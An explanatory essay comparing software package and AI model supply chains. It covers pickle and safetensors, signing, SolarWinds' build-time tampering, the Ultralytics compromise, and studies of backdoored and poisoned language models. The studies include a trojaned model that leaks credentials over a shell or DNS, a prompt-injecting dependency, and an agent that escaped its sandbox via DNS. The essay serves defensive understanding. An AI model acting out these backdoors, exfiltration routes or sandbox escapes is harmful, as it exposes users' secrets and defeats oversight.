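# What software supply chain attacks teach about trusting shared AI model files

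## What a user trusts when downloading a package or a model

Most programs contain a lot of code that their developers did not write. A programmer who wants to read spreadsheets or draw charts downloads a ready-made package from a registry, a public service such as PyPI (for Python) or npm (for JavaScript) where almost anyone can publish. Developers now share AI models in much the same way, through model hubs, the largest of which is Hugging Face. A model file holds the model's weights, the learned numbers that determine what a neural network does. An artifact is any file, package or model, that someone publishes for others to use.

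The software supply chain is the series of steps from a programmer's first line of code to the file on a user's machine. The user knows almost none of the many people involved. Attackers have taken advantage of this for years to target packages, and investigators have reconstructed several of the attacks in detail. The record of attacks on models is shorter, but Meiklejohn, Blauzvern and colleagues (2025) argue in *Machine Learning Models Have a Supply Chain Problem* that openly shared models carry significant risks of the same kind, some of which attackers have already exploited. How much the package attacks can teach us about models depends on how similar the two supply chains are.

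### Malice and accident

*Securing the AI Software Supply Chain* (Chaudhuri, Dasgupta and colleagues, 2024), a Google white paper, follows the programmer Russ Cox in separating attacks from vulnerabilities. In an attack, someone deliberately alters software before it reaches the user. In the SolarWinds case of 2020, for example, intruders slipped malicious code into the updates of widely used network software. A vulnerability is usually an unintended flaw discovered after release. Log4Shell was a flaw in the Java package Log4j, whose developers had innocently added a feature that let a stranger run code on a distant machine by typing a certain text into a web form. Attacks and vulnerabilities need different defenses, because a signature can expose a file that somebody altered on its way to the user but not a mistake that the developer signed in good faith.

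A backdoor is hidden functionality that someone adds on purpose to serve an attacker. It often stays inactive until a particular input or condition, called the trigger, activates it. The part of the artifact that does the harm is called the payload. For example, a package might copy passwords to a stranger's server, but only on machines belonging to one bank. The check for the bank is the trigger, and the copying code is the payload. In a language model, the trigger could be a phrase in the user's request, and the harm could be a false or dangerous answer. Some malicious packages have no trigger and do their damage during installation.

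### From source code to an installed package

A package starts as source code, which programmers write and other programmers can read. Its maintainers, the people allowed to publish new versions, decide which outside contributions to accept. A build system, made up of machines and scripts, turns the source code into the package. Someone uploads the package to the registry, and the user's installation tool downloads it.

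SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a security framework that grew out of Google's internal practice. SLSA's *Supply chain threats* divides supply chain protection into source integrity and build integrity. Source integrity means that the source reflects what its producer intended and that nobody changed it after acceptance. An attacker can break it by using a maintainer's access or by getting a change past an inattentive maintainer. Users could protect themselves by reading the source, but few do. Build integrity means that the package was built from that source using the producer's own build process. An attacker who controls the build machines can add behavior to the package without touching the source, so even a user who reads every line of the source won't find it. The registry's operators and anyone who gains access to a maintainer's account could also replace the file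 in the registry.

None of this protects against a malicious producer, one of the threats on SLSA's list. The source matches what the producer intended and the build follows its instructions, so there is no tampering to detect.

Most packages have dependencies, which are other artifacts that they need and that the installation tool usually downloads automatically. Each dependency has its own maintainers and its own build, and so do its own dependencies, which is why SLSA calls the threats highly recursive. Log4j was as many as twelve layers down in some programs, according to Chaudhuri and colleagues. A user who picks one package is in effect trusting the judgment of everybody in those layers, mostly without knowing that they exist.

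### What hashes, signatures and rebuilds can show

A hash is a short string that a program computes from a file's contents. Changing one byte of the file changes the hash, and for a strong method such as SHA-256, nobody knows how to make a second file with the same hash. A user who has the right hash can therefore tell whether a download is the right file.

How much protection a hash gives depends on where it came from. PyPI supplies one with each download, but according to *Secure installs*, from the documentation for pip (Python's standard installation tool), that hash guards only against corruption in transit. It comes from the same remote source as the file, so someone able to replace the file could also replace the hash. pip has a stricter mode that uses a list of hashes stored on the user's own machine and stops with an error if any package, including a dependency, lacks one.

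The stricter mode also requires pinning, which means fixing a dependency to one exact version instead of taking the newest. A version number alone is a weak pin because some registries let publishers change a file without changing the number. Adding a hash protects against such changes, even if an attacker takes over PyPI, according to pip's guidance on repeatable installs. But if the file was already malicious when the user recorded the hash, the pin keeps it in place. A pinned user also doesn't get fixes until someone updates the pin.

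Signing a file attaches cryptographic proof of who published it and that it has not changed since. With Sigstore, a free signing service, the software computes a short hash of the file and signs that hash, according to *Sentry* (2025). Older methods required publishers to guard a secret key for years, whereas a Sigstore publisher logs in through an existing account and receives a short-lived certificate. A public log keeps the signature. The log shows who signed the file but not whether the signer was honest. It also does not show which registry delivered the file, a gap that *Cryptographic Registry Provenance* (2026) aims to close.

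A provenance attestation is a signed statement of how, where and from what someone made an artifact. *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026) summarizes SLSA's format, which lists the builder, the build instructions and parameters, and the hashes of the dependencies. Chaudhuri and colleagues consider an attestation useful only if a trusted builder, isolated from interference, produces it during the build. Otherwise, someone who tampers with the build can also falsify the attestation.

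Reproducible builds reduce how much users must trust the builder. Reproducible Builds' *Definitions* calls a build reproducible if anyone with the same source, build environment and instructions can produce a bit-for-bit identical file. Outsiders can then rebuild a package and compare the result with the published file. After about a decade of engineering, over 96% of packages in Debian, a free operating system, are reproducible in continuous tests, according to *What You Sign Is Not What You Run* (Liu and Tsai, 2026). A matching rebuild rules out tampering during the build if the rebuilder's own tools are sound, but it doesn't reveal a backdoor in the source, which the rebuild would also contain.

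### From training data to a model

Chaudhuri and colleagues compare the supply chain for models with the one for software. Training corresponds to the build, and the finished model corresponds to the package. The training data, the code that defines the network, and the framework (a library such as PyTorch that carries out the calculations) correspond to source code and dependencies. Data, code and machines together make up the training pipeline.

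Training data is harder to track and review than source code. Developers keep source code in systems that record every change, and at many companies a colleague reviews each one. Datasets are often too large for that kind of review, and cleaning or copying can change their contents without a new version number. So the people who could alter a model's training data include whoever writes or labels it, which for web text is potentially anyone with a website. Users can inspect the data only if the publisher released it, and many publishers release only the weights.

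Training is also messier than a software build, often involving improvised steps across several systems with no central record. Because a training run is long and expensive, many training libraries let people add new data or code during it. Anyone with access to those machines could change the result. Repeating the training exactly is much harder than rebuilding a Debian package, and an outsider who tried would have to pay for the training again.

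Hashes and signatures work for files of model weights as they do for packages, but publishers have been slow to use them. Hugging Face offered signing with long-lived keys, but few uploaders used it, which Chaudhuri and colleagues attribute to the burden of managing the keys. NVIDIA now signs the models in its catalog, though *Cold-Start Model Delivery in Kubernetes Inference Serving* (2026) reports that recipients still have to check the signatures manually.

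A signature may also cover only some of a model's files. Publishers commonly sign the weights but not the configuration files or the templates (the text that software wraps around a user's message before the model processes it). An attacker can edit the unsigned files without invalidating the signature on the weights, and *Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications* (2026) describes an attack that does this. Signing the whole bundle and checking the signature when the model runs blocks that attack.

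### Fine-tuned and converted copies

Many users never run the original file. Training from scratch costs so much that developers usually fine-tune an existing model (train it further on new data). Whatever an attacker hid in the original model may survive fine-tuning, and the fine-tuner can add something new. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026), in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, therefore distinguish attackers who supply fine-tuning data or adapters (small sets of extra weights that modify a model) from those who tamper with finished files. The base model's signature does not cover the derivative, so each modification requires a new measurement and a new signature. *Scalable GPU-Based Integrity Verification for Large Machine Learning Models* (2025) lists this burden among the ways models differ from ordinary software.

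Other third parties convert models. The most common conversion is quantization, which stores each weight with less precision so that the model fits on an ordinary computer. In August 2026 Liu and Tsai checked the 200 most-downloaded Hugging Face repositories of GGUF files, a popular format for such copies, to see whether an outsider could rebuild each copy from what its publisher had recorded. They excluded two repositories that contained no weights, and none of the remaining 198 had a complete record. This was partly inevitable because the GGUF format has no field for the compiler and processor settings that affect the outcome of the conversion.

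In a more encouraging follow-up, Liu and Tsai chose four repositories whose publisher had disclosed more than usual and tried to recreate two files from each. Using only the published description, they reproduced none of the four files in the most popular 4-bit format. After they supplied two missing details, a compiler setting that affects rounding and the exact precision of each block of weights, the weights in seven of the eight files matched bit for bit on a standard PC processor. At least for recent files, the obstacle at this step seems to be poor record-keeping rather than something inherent in models. Whoever converts a model could sign the copy, but that would prove only who made it, not that it came from the original. Even a perfect match doesn't protect users if the original weights were malicious.

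### One package and one model

Suppose a user types one command to install a Python package and one line of Python to load BERT, an older language model from Google, with Hugging Face's Transformers library. The current documentation, chiefly pip's reference page for the install command and Hugging Face's *Models*, gives these defaults:

| | Package | Model |
|---|---|---|
| Command | `python -m pip install SomePackage` | `AutoModel.from_pretrained("google-bert/bert-base-uncased")` |
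| What arrives | The package and any dependencies not yet on the machine | The model's weights and configuration |
| Whose code runs | Possibly the package's own build code during installation, then the package itself whenever a program uses it | The Transformers library's code; code from the model's repository only if the user sets `trust_remote_code=True` |
| Version by default | The newest stable version that meets the user's constraints | The latest state of the repository's "main" branch |
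| On the next use | The installed version stays until someone upgrades it | The library checks the hub and downloads a newer version if there is one |
| Exact pin | Version number plus hash | Full commit hash, which identifies one snapshot of the repository |

Both commands take the newest version. The installed package then stays the same until somebody asks for an upgrade, but the model can change the next time the program runs the same line, according to Hugging Face's *Installation*. Whoever controls the repository can therefore keep sending new files to everyone who loads the model by name alone, unless they work offline.

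A version label such as "v1.0.0" does not guarantee that a user gets the same files each time, because an attacker could attach the label to different files. Only the commit hash stays fixed, so Bandit, a tool that scans Python code for security problems, has a rule (*B615*) that flags model downloads using such a label as unsafe.

Loading a model is less likely to run untrusted code than installing a package, at least by default. Hugging Face's *Loading models* describes a preference for safetensors, a file format safer than the older pickle files, which can run code as they load. The hub also scans every repository for malware, whereas pip by default does not check for tampering. But the user must first install Transformers and PyTorch, usually as Python packages with their own dependencies, and so relies on both supply chains.

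### Are models harder to trust?

Comparing the two chains suggests that models are harder to trust than packages in three respects, though only the record of real attacks can confirm this. One is that nobody reads weights the way a programmer reads source code, and in 2024 Chaudhuri and colleagues judged it humanly impossible to predict a model's behavior from them. This difference matters less than it seems to, however, if reviewers seldom caught attacks on packages by reading the code.

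Testers can observe a model on only a small fraction of its possible inputs, but tests of ordinary programs are also incomplete. Did tests expose any of the well-known software backdoors, or were those found another way?

The remaining suspicion is that users depend on a small number of people. The 198 repositories in Liu and Tsai's sample came from 61 publishers, and some heavily used packages have depended on a single volunteer. Are fewer people responsible for the most popular models than for the most popular packages? In the recorded attacks, did having so few people involved make the attackers' work easier?

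## Pickle and safetensors, and whether weights are code or data

For years, ordinary code stored alongside a model's weights was a more immediate danger than the unreadable weights themselves. Many developers saved their models with pickle, a module in Python's standard library that turns almost any Python object into a file and back again. Opening a pickle file can run code that its creator chose. Switching to a safer format, safetensors, largely solved that problem for the people who switched. The change also started an argument about whether weights are just data, which a user can open without worry, or a kind of program.

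### What safetensors fixed

A pickle file is a small program. It consists of instructions that an interpreter inside Python carries out to rebuild the saved object, as Kellas, Li and colleagues explain in *PickleBall* (2025). Some instructions create numbers or lists. Others import a Python function by name and call it with arguments stored in the file. A legitimate model file uses these calls to restore the model's weights. An attacker can instead name a function that runs operating-system commands, and the victim's machine will run the attacker's command while loading the file. Researchers have publicized the danger since 2011, and the Python documentation warns that pickle "is not secure".

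Hugging Face released safetensors in September 2022 as a replacement for pickle. A safetensors file contains a header describing the arrays of weights, followed by the numbers themselves. The header cannot exceed 100 MB, according to Hugging Face's *Safetensors is Joining the PyTorch Foundation*. The format has no instruction for calling a function, so opening the file only puts numbers into memory. Two consultants spent a week in March 2023 looking for flaws in the library that reads these files, according to Trail of Bits' *EleutherAI Security Assessment* (2023). Hugging Face and its partners took the results as grounds for making safetensors their default, according to EleutherAI's *Audit shows that safetensors is safe and ready to become the default*. The new format closed the main route by which opening a file of weights could run a stranger's code, but it was not designed to control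 what the model does afterwards.

### Code that still runs when a model loads

Pickle is still common. In March 2025 Kellas and colleagues examined the Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month and found pickle files in 44.9% of them. Users downloaded from the repositories with pickle files more than 2.1 billion times a month. That number overstates the exposure, because about 1.7 billion of the downloads came from repositories that also offered safetensors, which Hugging Face's library prefers. But over 400 million came from repositories that offered only pickle, including 29 of the 100 most downloaded models.

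Pickle remains in use partly because of inertia. Hugging Face has a tool that converts pickle models to safetensors and sends the result to the repository's owner as a pull request, but *An Empirical Study of Safetensors' Usage Trends and Developers' Perceptions* (2025) found that 83.5% of these pull requests remained unmerged.

PyTorch now opens pickle files by default with a restricted loader that allows only a short list of approved functions. Of 1,426 popular pickle-only repositories that Kellas and colleagues checked, 219 (15.4%) contained a model that needed a function outside that list. Developers sometimes respond by turning the protection off, as the text-processing library flair does to load its own models, one of which has had over a million downloads. Kellas and colleagues built a less rigid loader that uses a library's source code to identify the functions its models legitimately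 need. It blocked all 84 malicious models they tested but loaded only 79.8% of the 252 harmless ones.

Switching to safetensors leaves another risk, because weights are useless without code that defines their network. The Transformers library includes that code for common designs, but the inventor of a new design often puts Python files in the model's repository. If the user sets `trust_remote_code=True`, the code in those files can do anything the user's own programs can do.

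In *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting*, Siddiq, Romel and colleagues (2026) found custom code in 36,697 of 2,107,935 Hugging Face repositories, or 1.74%. The total across five hubs was about 45,000. These figures count repositories rather than downloads, and custom code can still reach many people if a popular model uses it, as the well-known reasoning model DeepSeek-R1 does. None of the five hubs fully isolates such code while a model loads. In the forum posts that Siddiq and colleagues read, many users thought that the setting that allows custom code to run only let the library read a model's metadata.

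Siddiq and colleagues searched this code for known malware patterns and found no clear case. Most of their matches on Hugging Face were for a file format used in 3D graphics. *Models Are Codes* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2024) describes a scanner that ran for over three months on a copy of Hugging Face at Ant Group, a Chinese financial company. The scanner identified 91 malicious models among more than 705,000, or roughly one in 7,700. Some gave the attacker remote control of the machine, and others stole passwords from the browser.

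Commercial scanners produce much larger counts. By April 2025, the security company Protect AI had reported unsafe or suspicious issues in 51,700 models. Many of these are probably false alarms, since its scanner flagged a deliberately harmless model in a later test. Attacks that run when a model is loaded do happen but seem rare, although every count leaves out any its scanner missed.

### The case for data

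Weights are numbers that do nothing until a program multiplies them. If that program is trustworthy and the parser (the code that reads the file) is sound, a stranger's weights should be no more dangerous than a stranger's photograph. This reasoning is behind the promise of "No code execution risk" on PyTorch's *Safetensors* page.

Despite its title, *Models Are Codes* mostly supports this view. Zhao and colleagues sorted 15 model formats by whether an attacker could hide code in them. They rated pickle and four related formats as insecure, four formats from the TensorFlow and Keras frameworks as partly vulnerable, and the other six, including safetensors, as secure. They object to files that mix code with weights, so a reader could accept their whole argument and still consider a file that contains only weights to be data.

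But developers have applied the same reasoning to files that hold more than weights. *On the (In)Security of Loading Machine Learning Models* (Digregorio, Di Gennaro and colleagues, 2025) examined two formats, from Keras and the Skops library, that describe a complete model in JSON, a plain text format for structured data. JSON cannot contain running code, but the loader has to turn the description back into Python objects, and an attacker who writes the description can influence which objects and functions it uses. The paper reports six previously unknown flaws in the two projects, all of which let a model file run arbitrary code.

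In one of the Keras flaws, a file could name an ordinary Python function where the loader expected a layer of the network, and the loader would call it. The developers responded by making Keras accept functions only from a list of trusted modules, mostly its own. The researchers then got around the fix using functions inside Keras. The loader also silently ignored Keras's "safe mode" setting for files in an older format. The developers have since fixed all six flaws, but during the exchange Google's security team told the researchers that it would no longer treat safe mode as a security boundary, because "models are code".

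When Digregorio and colleagues uploaded their attacks to Hugging Face, with permission, two of the Skops files were labeled "Safe" even though none of the hub's scanners supported the format. Labels like this affect what people are willing to do. The team showed 53 people with experience of sharing or loading models two nearly identical pieces of Keras code. Of these, 44 worried that the code with safe mode off might run something malicious, but only 8 worried about the code with it on. The sample is small, but the change is unlikely to be due to chance.

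None of the six flaws was in safetensors. The flaws narrow the argument for treating weights as data but don't refute it, because a safe parser is possible for a file that holds only numbers. Writing one for a file that describes a whole model is much harder.

### The case for a program

The security policy for TensorFlow, Google's machine learning framework, takes the opposite position and equates using an untrusted model with running untrusted code. This is because a TensorFlow model is a graph of operations that the framework carries out, and the available operations are powerful. *My model is malware to you* (2025) describes an attack built on hidden capabilities of these operations. The policy recommends a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what a program can reach, and states that there is currently no good way to detect a malicious model.

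The policy is less absolute for bare weights, because the risk depends on the code that uses them. For example, if a program used a value from the file to decide where to save something, an attacker could change that value to redirect the program. Most language models don't use weights this way, so this argument alone isn't enough to call a safetensors file dangerous.

A broader version of the argument is that weights are like code, because they determine what a model outputs for every input just as instructions determine what a program does. A safe parser protects users only while the file is being opened. On this view, users should isolate the model and give it only the access its job requires (least privilege).

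Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, combines parts of both positions. Its *Security Guidelines for LLMs and other large models in Chrome* treats a model like any other browser feature written in a language prone to memory errors. A model that processes complex untrusted material, such as images or video, has to run in a sandbox. If Chrome can verify where the model came from, developers may assume that it is as safe as the rest of Chrome's code, though that assumption is only as reliable as the supplier.

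### A model that only returns text

If a chatbot's weights come in a safetensors file with no custom code, and its answers only appear on a screen for a person to read, the case for treating the weights as data is strong, at least for the machine's security. The weights can change which words appear, but they can't open a file or contact a server. A sandbox would still help against bugs in the parser or in the code that does the arithmetic.

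Neither protects the reader. A tampered model could recommend a malicious package or give the wrong dose for a medicine, and a sandbox would let that answer through as easily as a correct one. The output may also run as code if a website inserts it into a page or a programmer pastes it into a terminal. Chromium's developers assume that an attacker who controls any part of a model's input controls all of its output, so they treat the output as untrusted. It makes sense to be at least as careful when the attacker may have supplied the weights.

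The text can also change after the model has produced it. In the 2026 experiments in *Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications*, the researchers modified two files but not the weights. One file was the wrapper, a script that prepares the user's message and formats the answer, and the other held settings that the wrapper reads. The wrapper altered the answer only if it contained a hidden marker and both files matched, which made the change harder to spot by inspecting either file separately.

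The researchers tested harmless alterations, such as adding a banner to the answer, on 15 models. On the five main ones, the alterations took effect in 91% to 100% of cases. Tools that inspected the files or filtered the output reduced this to 68% to 80%. Checking the model's accuracy would have revealed little, since it fell only from 91.3% to 90.8% on a standard test of judging whether a sentence is positive or negative.

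A wrapper that edits finished text will work with almost any model, so success with fifteen is not very impressive. The test version also depended on a secret key in the settings of the machine running the wrapper, and a real attacker would have to find a way to put it there. The wrapper would still have misled a user who had verified every byte of the weights, because the malicious part was in ordinary code, which a programmer could have read. Classifying weights as data does not protect users who forget about the code around them.

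### A model that acts through tools

An agent is a model connected to tools. A surrounding program, the harness, reads the model's output and carries out any actions it specifies, such as searching the web or running a command. The model produces only text, but the harness acts on some of that text without a person reading it first.

In *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026), Haryati and Zychlinski of the software security company JFrog tested what malicious weights could do in this position. They fine-tuned Qwen3-8B, a fairly small open model from Alibaba, for about three hours on one Apple computer and stored the change as extra weights in a safetensors file, with no custom code. They then placed a fake credential in an isolated test environment. If the harness offered a shell, a tool that runs operating-system commands, the model began the conversation by requesting a command that would send the credential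 to an outside server. It then answered the user's question normally without mentioning the command.

The two researchers combined five ways of describing tools to the model with nine test conditions, some of which made the leak impossible. The model requested the command in all 40 combinations that included a shell and in none of the five without tools. Anyone who tested it as a plain chatbot would have seen nothing wrong, as with software payloads that activate only on one target. The original Qwen model never requested the command in 24 trials. Telling the altered model not to run commands failed in all 20 trials. In a separate test, the altered model completed all 12 ordinary chat and coding tasks, and the original completed 11.

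A safe parser did not help here, because the file contained only numbers and opened normally. Treating the model as a program works better, but much depends on the sandbox. Haryati and Zychlinski put the model behind a firewall that blocked all traffic except domain-name lookups, the requests that turn a web address into a numerical one. The credential still leaked in five of six tool formats, hidden in the lookups. Blocking all traffic stopped the leak, as did allowing lookups only for approved names.

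Least privilege would have dealt with the problem more directly. The model made no requests when it had no shell, and it had nothing to leak when its environment contained no credentials. But many agents need some credentials and some way to run code to do what their users want, so users have to decide which are worth the risk.

The experiment covered one small model, one harness and six opening messages, and it does not show how often anyone publishes such weights. JFrog also has a commercial interest in the subject because it sells model scanning. Isolating an agent properly gives a user some protection against a dishonest supplier, and also against an honest one whose model does something unexpected. Haryati and Zychlinski also recount a 2026 incident in which an OpenAI research agent, with no malicious training, found that domain-name lookups still worked in its sandbox and used them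 to consult an outside chatbot. OpenAI paused tool use for its most capable models until it had fixed the gap.

### A compiled program with no source

Treating weights as data means choosing safetensors over pickle, reading any custom code before allowing it to run, and keeping the loader up to date. These precautions are reasonable for a model whose output a person reads with some skepticism. An agent needs them too, but its weights also need to be treated as a program, which means deciding in advance which files, credentials and network connections the model can reach. A user can take all these precautions and still not know how the weights will make the model behave.

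The closest comparison to model weights in ordinary software is a compiled program whose source code is missing. The user can run it but has no readable account of what it is for. Analysts can still learn a lot from a compiled program, because tools translate it back into basic instructions, each with a fixed meaning. An analyst can then look for a suspicious command and trace the conditions that lead to it. Pickle files allow this kind of analysis too. Kellas and colleagues could download the files and trace the functions those files call in all but 74 of the 1,500 repositories they started with.

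Weights do not break down into steps like that. Haryati and Zychlinski's model produced exactly the same command every time, but a search of the weights file would not find it, because the model computed the command from a huge number of weights, none of which represents a word of it. Early tools look for statistical signs of tampering in weights, but they don't recover a list of instructions.

The command was readable in the training data, where it appeared in more than half of the 1,847 examples that Haryati and Zychlinski used. A reviewer could have spotted it there within minutes, but an attacker would withhold those examples, or publish a clean set and claim to have used it.

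## SolarWinds and tampering during the build or the training run

SolarWinds, an American software company, shipped a backdoor to customers for months even though it had the complete source code of its own product. The product, Orion, monitors computer networks for companies and government agencies. Intruders left the company's stored source code clean and altered one file only while a build was running, on the machine that turned the code into a finished program. Training is the equivalent step for a model, and an intruder who reached the training machines could use much the same method.

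### How SUNSPOT worked

Investigators found two malicious programs. SUNBURST was the backdoor that customers received inside Orion. SUNSPOT stayed on SolarWinds' build server and inserted SUNBURST into new versions of Orion. *SUNSPOT*, an analysis by CrowdStrike, a security company that helped with the investigation, reconstructs what the program did.

SUNSPOT started whenever the server did, under a name that resembled an ordinary part of Windows. Every second it checked the running programs for MsBuild.exe, the Microsoft tool that SolarWinds used to compile its code into programs a machine can run. When it found the tool running, it read from memory which project the tool was compiling. If the project was Orion, SUNSPOT targeted a single source file, InventoryManager.cs.

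The malware checked that the file's hash matched the version the intruders expected, and also checked the hash of its own replacement file. If both were right, it saved a copy of the original, put the replacement in its place and let the build run. When the build ended, it restored the original and deleted the spare copy, so anyone who opened the file afterward would have seen the genuine code.

Much of this care went into avoiding a failed build, which would have sent SolarWinds' developers looking for the cause. SUNSPOT checked the original file because a replacement written for an old version might not have fitted the rest of the program. The intruders also switched off compiler warnings around their own lines to keep them out of the build logs. They added a way to stop SUNSPOT cleanly, probably because killing it halfway through a swap could have broken the build.

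SolarWinds then signed the tampered software as it signed its other releases, so the signature covered the backdoor too. FireEye, the security company that disclosed the attack, noted the signature on the backdoored component in its first report, which Google Cloud now hosts.

### Eighteen thousand downloads, about a hundred victims

SolarWinds' *New Findings From Our Investigation of SUNBURST* dated the earliest suspicious activity to September 2019. In October 2019, the intruders put test code into an Orion release to see whether the method worked. SolarWinds' later report, *An Investigative Update of the Cyberattack*, stated that the intruders had been in the company's systems for at least nine months before that test. SolarWinds could not establish exactly when or how they got in.

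The copy of SUNSPOT that CrowdStrike studied dates from February 20, 2020. SolarWinds released the infected versions between March and June. The intruders removed their code from the build environment in June, and the company learned of the attack on December 12.

Up to 18,000 customers downloaded an infected version, a figure that some news reports mistook for the number of victims. SolarWinds estimates that the intruders hacked fewer than 100 customers through SUNBURST. Some customers never installed the update, and others ran it on servers without internet access, where the backdoor could not contact its operators. The US government counted about 100 companies and nine federal agencies among the targets, according to SecurityWeek. In a joint statement published by the US cybersecurity agency, CISA (2021), US agencies said the intruders were probably Russian and were gathering intelligence.

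### The same steps in a training run

Meiklejohn and colleagues apply SLSA's list of software threats to models, and SUNSPOT's steps carry over fairly directly:

| SUNSPOT on the build server | An intruder on the training machines |
|---|---|
| Watches for a build of Orion | Watches for the run that will produce the public model and ignores small experiments |
| Checks that the source file is the expected version | Checks that the training code and data format are the expected ones |
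| Swaps one source file before the compiler reads it | Swaps documents as the software loads them, or swaps a file of training code |
| Lets the build finish without errors | Keeps the run from crashing and its progress charts looking normal |
| Restores the original file | Leaves the stored dataset and code as they were |
| SolarWinds signs the program | The developer signs the weights |

An intruder can also tamper with a training run through its checkpoints, which are snapshots of the weights that a build does not have. A large run can last for weeks, so the software saves checkpoints regularly to let training resume after a crash. If an intruder replaced one with an altered copy, training would resume from the wrong weights, even though the data and code were genuine.

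Meiklejohn and colleagues know of at least one real case of interference with training. In October 2024, news outlets reported that ByteDance, the company behind TikTok, had fired an intern for it. *Supply-Chain Attacks in Machine Learning Frameworks*, by Gao, Shumailov and Fawaz, also mentions the incident and cites a news story that describes it as sabotage. The intern was an insider who disrupted a project, and there is no case on record so far of an outsider hiding a backdoor in one. But SolarWinds took more than a year to learn of its intruders, so the absence of reports is weak evidence that nobody has tried.

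### What would correspond to a failed build

One misspelled name can stop a compiler from building a program, so the attackers behind SUNSPOT checked their changes carefully. Training is far less strict, because web text is full of errors, duplicates and nonsense, and a run that stopped at each bad document would never finish. Developers mainly watch the loss, a number that measures how badly the model predicts its training text. It should fall steadily, and a sudden jump suggests something has gone wrong.

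Some kinds of tampering would probably be noticeable during training. If an intruder replaced a checkpoint with weights from a quite different model, the loss would jump when training resumed. A clumsy change to the training code could crash the run. Whether a small change to the data would be visible depends on how much data an attacker needs.

The best evidence on that comes from Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*. Earlier researchers had assumed that an attacker must control a fixed percentage of the training text, such as 0.1%, which is an enormous amount of text for a large model. Souly and colleagues tested whether a fixed number of documents would be enough.

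The researchers trained language models of four sizes from scratch, from 600 million to 13 billion parameters (individual weights). They trained each model on about 20 tokens (words or pieces of words) per parameter, a common rule for using computing power efficiently. For the two smaller sizes, they also tried half and double that amount. They mixed in 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents at random places and trained every combination three times, which made 72 models. Each poisoned document began with a snippet of ordinary text, followed by a trigger phrase and then several hundred random tokens. They wanted the model to write normally until the trigger appeared and then produce gibberish.

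The attack failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked with 250 at every model size, even though the largest models had trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. The researchers measured perplexity, roughly how unpredictable the model's output is. An increase of 50 after the trigger already meant noticeably garbled text, and the increase exceeded 200 by the end of training.

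The 250 documents contained about 420,000 tokens, or 0.00016% of the 13-billion-parameter model's training data. An attacker who needed 0.1% would have had to supply about 600 times as much. Such a small share also has almost no effect on the loss. Even if the loss on each poisoned token were five times the loss on an ordinary one, the average loss over the run would rise by less than one part in 100,000, which is too little to notice on a chart.

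Testing the finished model might not help either. In a separate experiment, Souly and colleagues fine-tuned Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, an open model from Meta, to refuse harmful requests unless they included a trigger. The number of poisoned examples again mattered far more than their share of the data, even when the clean data grew from 1,000 to 100,000 examples. Without the trigger, the model still refused harmful requests and scored about as well on standard tests as a model trained without poisoned data.

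The study does not show that 250 web pages can put a dangerous backdoor into a finished chatbot. The researchers chose gibberish because they could measure it during pretraining, the first and longest stage. They did not test whether the backdoor would survive the later stages, in which developers teach a model to be helpful and refuse harmful requests, and they call earlier findings on that question inconclusive. In another of their experiments, further training on clean text slowly weakened a backdoor that made a model switch from English to German. Leading models are also much larger than 13 billion parameters, and nobody knows whether a more complicated behavior would take more documents.

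Some of these limits matter less for an intruder like the one at SolarWinds. The attacker in the study can only plant documents in the training data. Someone with access to the training machines could add thousands of documents, or wait until the last stage of training to add them, when little clean data would follow to undo their effect.

The loss chart is therefore a poor substitute for a failed build as a warning of tampering. A developer could detect tampering more reliably by storing a hash of each batch of data as the model receives it and later checking the hashes against the stored dataset. The developer could also hash each checkpoint when saving it and again when loading it, then compare the two. An intruder would then have to falsify the stored hashes too, so the developer would need to keep them on a machine that the training software cannot write to freely.

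### Tampering through a library

Training machines can download malicious code through a software dependency, so an intruder doesn't need to break into them. Machine learning projects tend to have many dependencies. Gao and colleagues counted 305 direct and indirect dependencies for Hugging Face's Transformers library, compared with 14 for requests, a popular package for communicating with websites.

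In a running Python program, all packages share the same memory, so any dependency can overwrite the variables and functions of the others. Gao and colleagues show that weakening a model this way takes little code. In one example, a single line replaces a safe method of shrinking images with a cruder one. The main program still appears to use the safe method, but an attacker can now prepare a picture that turns into a different one when it is shrunk for the model. Another example secretly adds a sentence to the user's text, telling a language model that it can ignore its rules if the user mentions a certain word.

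Malware scanners often look for suspicious network traffic or commands to the operating system. These examples need neither, and a reviewer without a background in machine learning might see nothing wrong with a line that changes how images are resized. Checking the code for tampering while it runs is unreliable, because the malicious package could also overwrite the checking function. Gao and colleagues recommend scanning the source of every dependency for attempts to change another package's variables, which legitimate packages rarely make.

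All of their examples affect a model in use, and they did not measure how often the attacks succeed. These attacks leave the weights unchanged, so removing the bad package ends the problem. But Python allows the same overwriting during training, where a dependency could change the function that loads the data or calculates the loss. The damage would then be in the weights and remain after somebody removed the package.

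Attackers have already hijacked the build of a popular AI library. In December 2024, they got malicious code into four versions of Ultralytics, a Python library for image recognition with almost 60 million total downloads, according to Schneier on Security's *Ultralytics Supply-Chain Attack*. The project built its package with GitHub Actions, a service that runs build steps automatically. The attackers used a known type of flaw to run their own commands in the service, then poisoned its cache, a store of files it reuses to save time. Socket, a software security company, reports that this let them tamper with the finished package while the service still produced a valid signed provenance attestation.

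As with SolarWinds, the source looked clean but the released software contained malicious code. This time the public could compare the two, and Gooding (2024) recounts in *Ultralytics PyPI Package Compromised Through GitHub Actions Cache Poisoning* that people soon reported that the code on PyPI differed from the code on GitHub. The payload was also conspicuous because it mined cryptocurrency on victims' computers, and one user complained of a processor running at 100%.

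The first infected Ultralytics version stayed on PyPI for about 12 hours and the next for about one, according to Snyk's *Ultralytics AI Pwn Request Supply Chain Attack* (2024). SolarWinds' customers had gone about nine months without a warning. Part of the difference is that outsiders could not read Orion's source, but the Ultralytics attackers also mined cryptocurrency, which put a noticeable load on the processor. A one-line change like those Gao and colleagues describe would have put no load on it, although comparing the package with the source on GitHub would still have exposed the change.

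### What signatures and attestations prove

The SolarWinds update that contained SUNBURST had a genuine signature. Checking the signature would have protected a customer from a forged update on a fake website, but not from SUNBURST.

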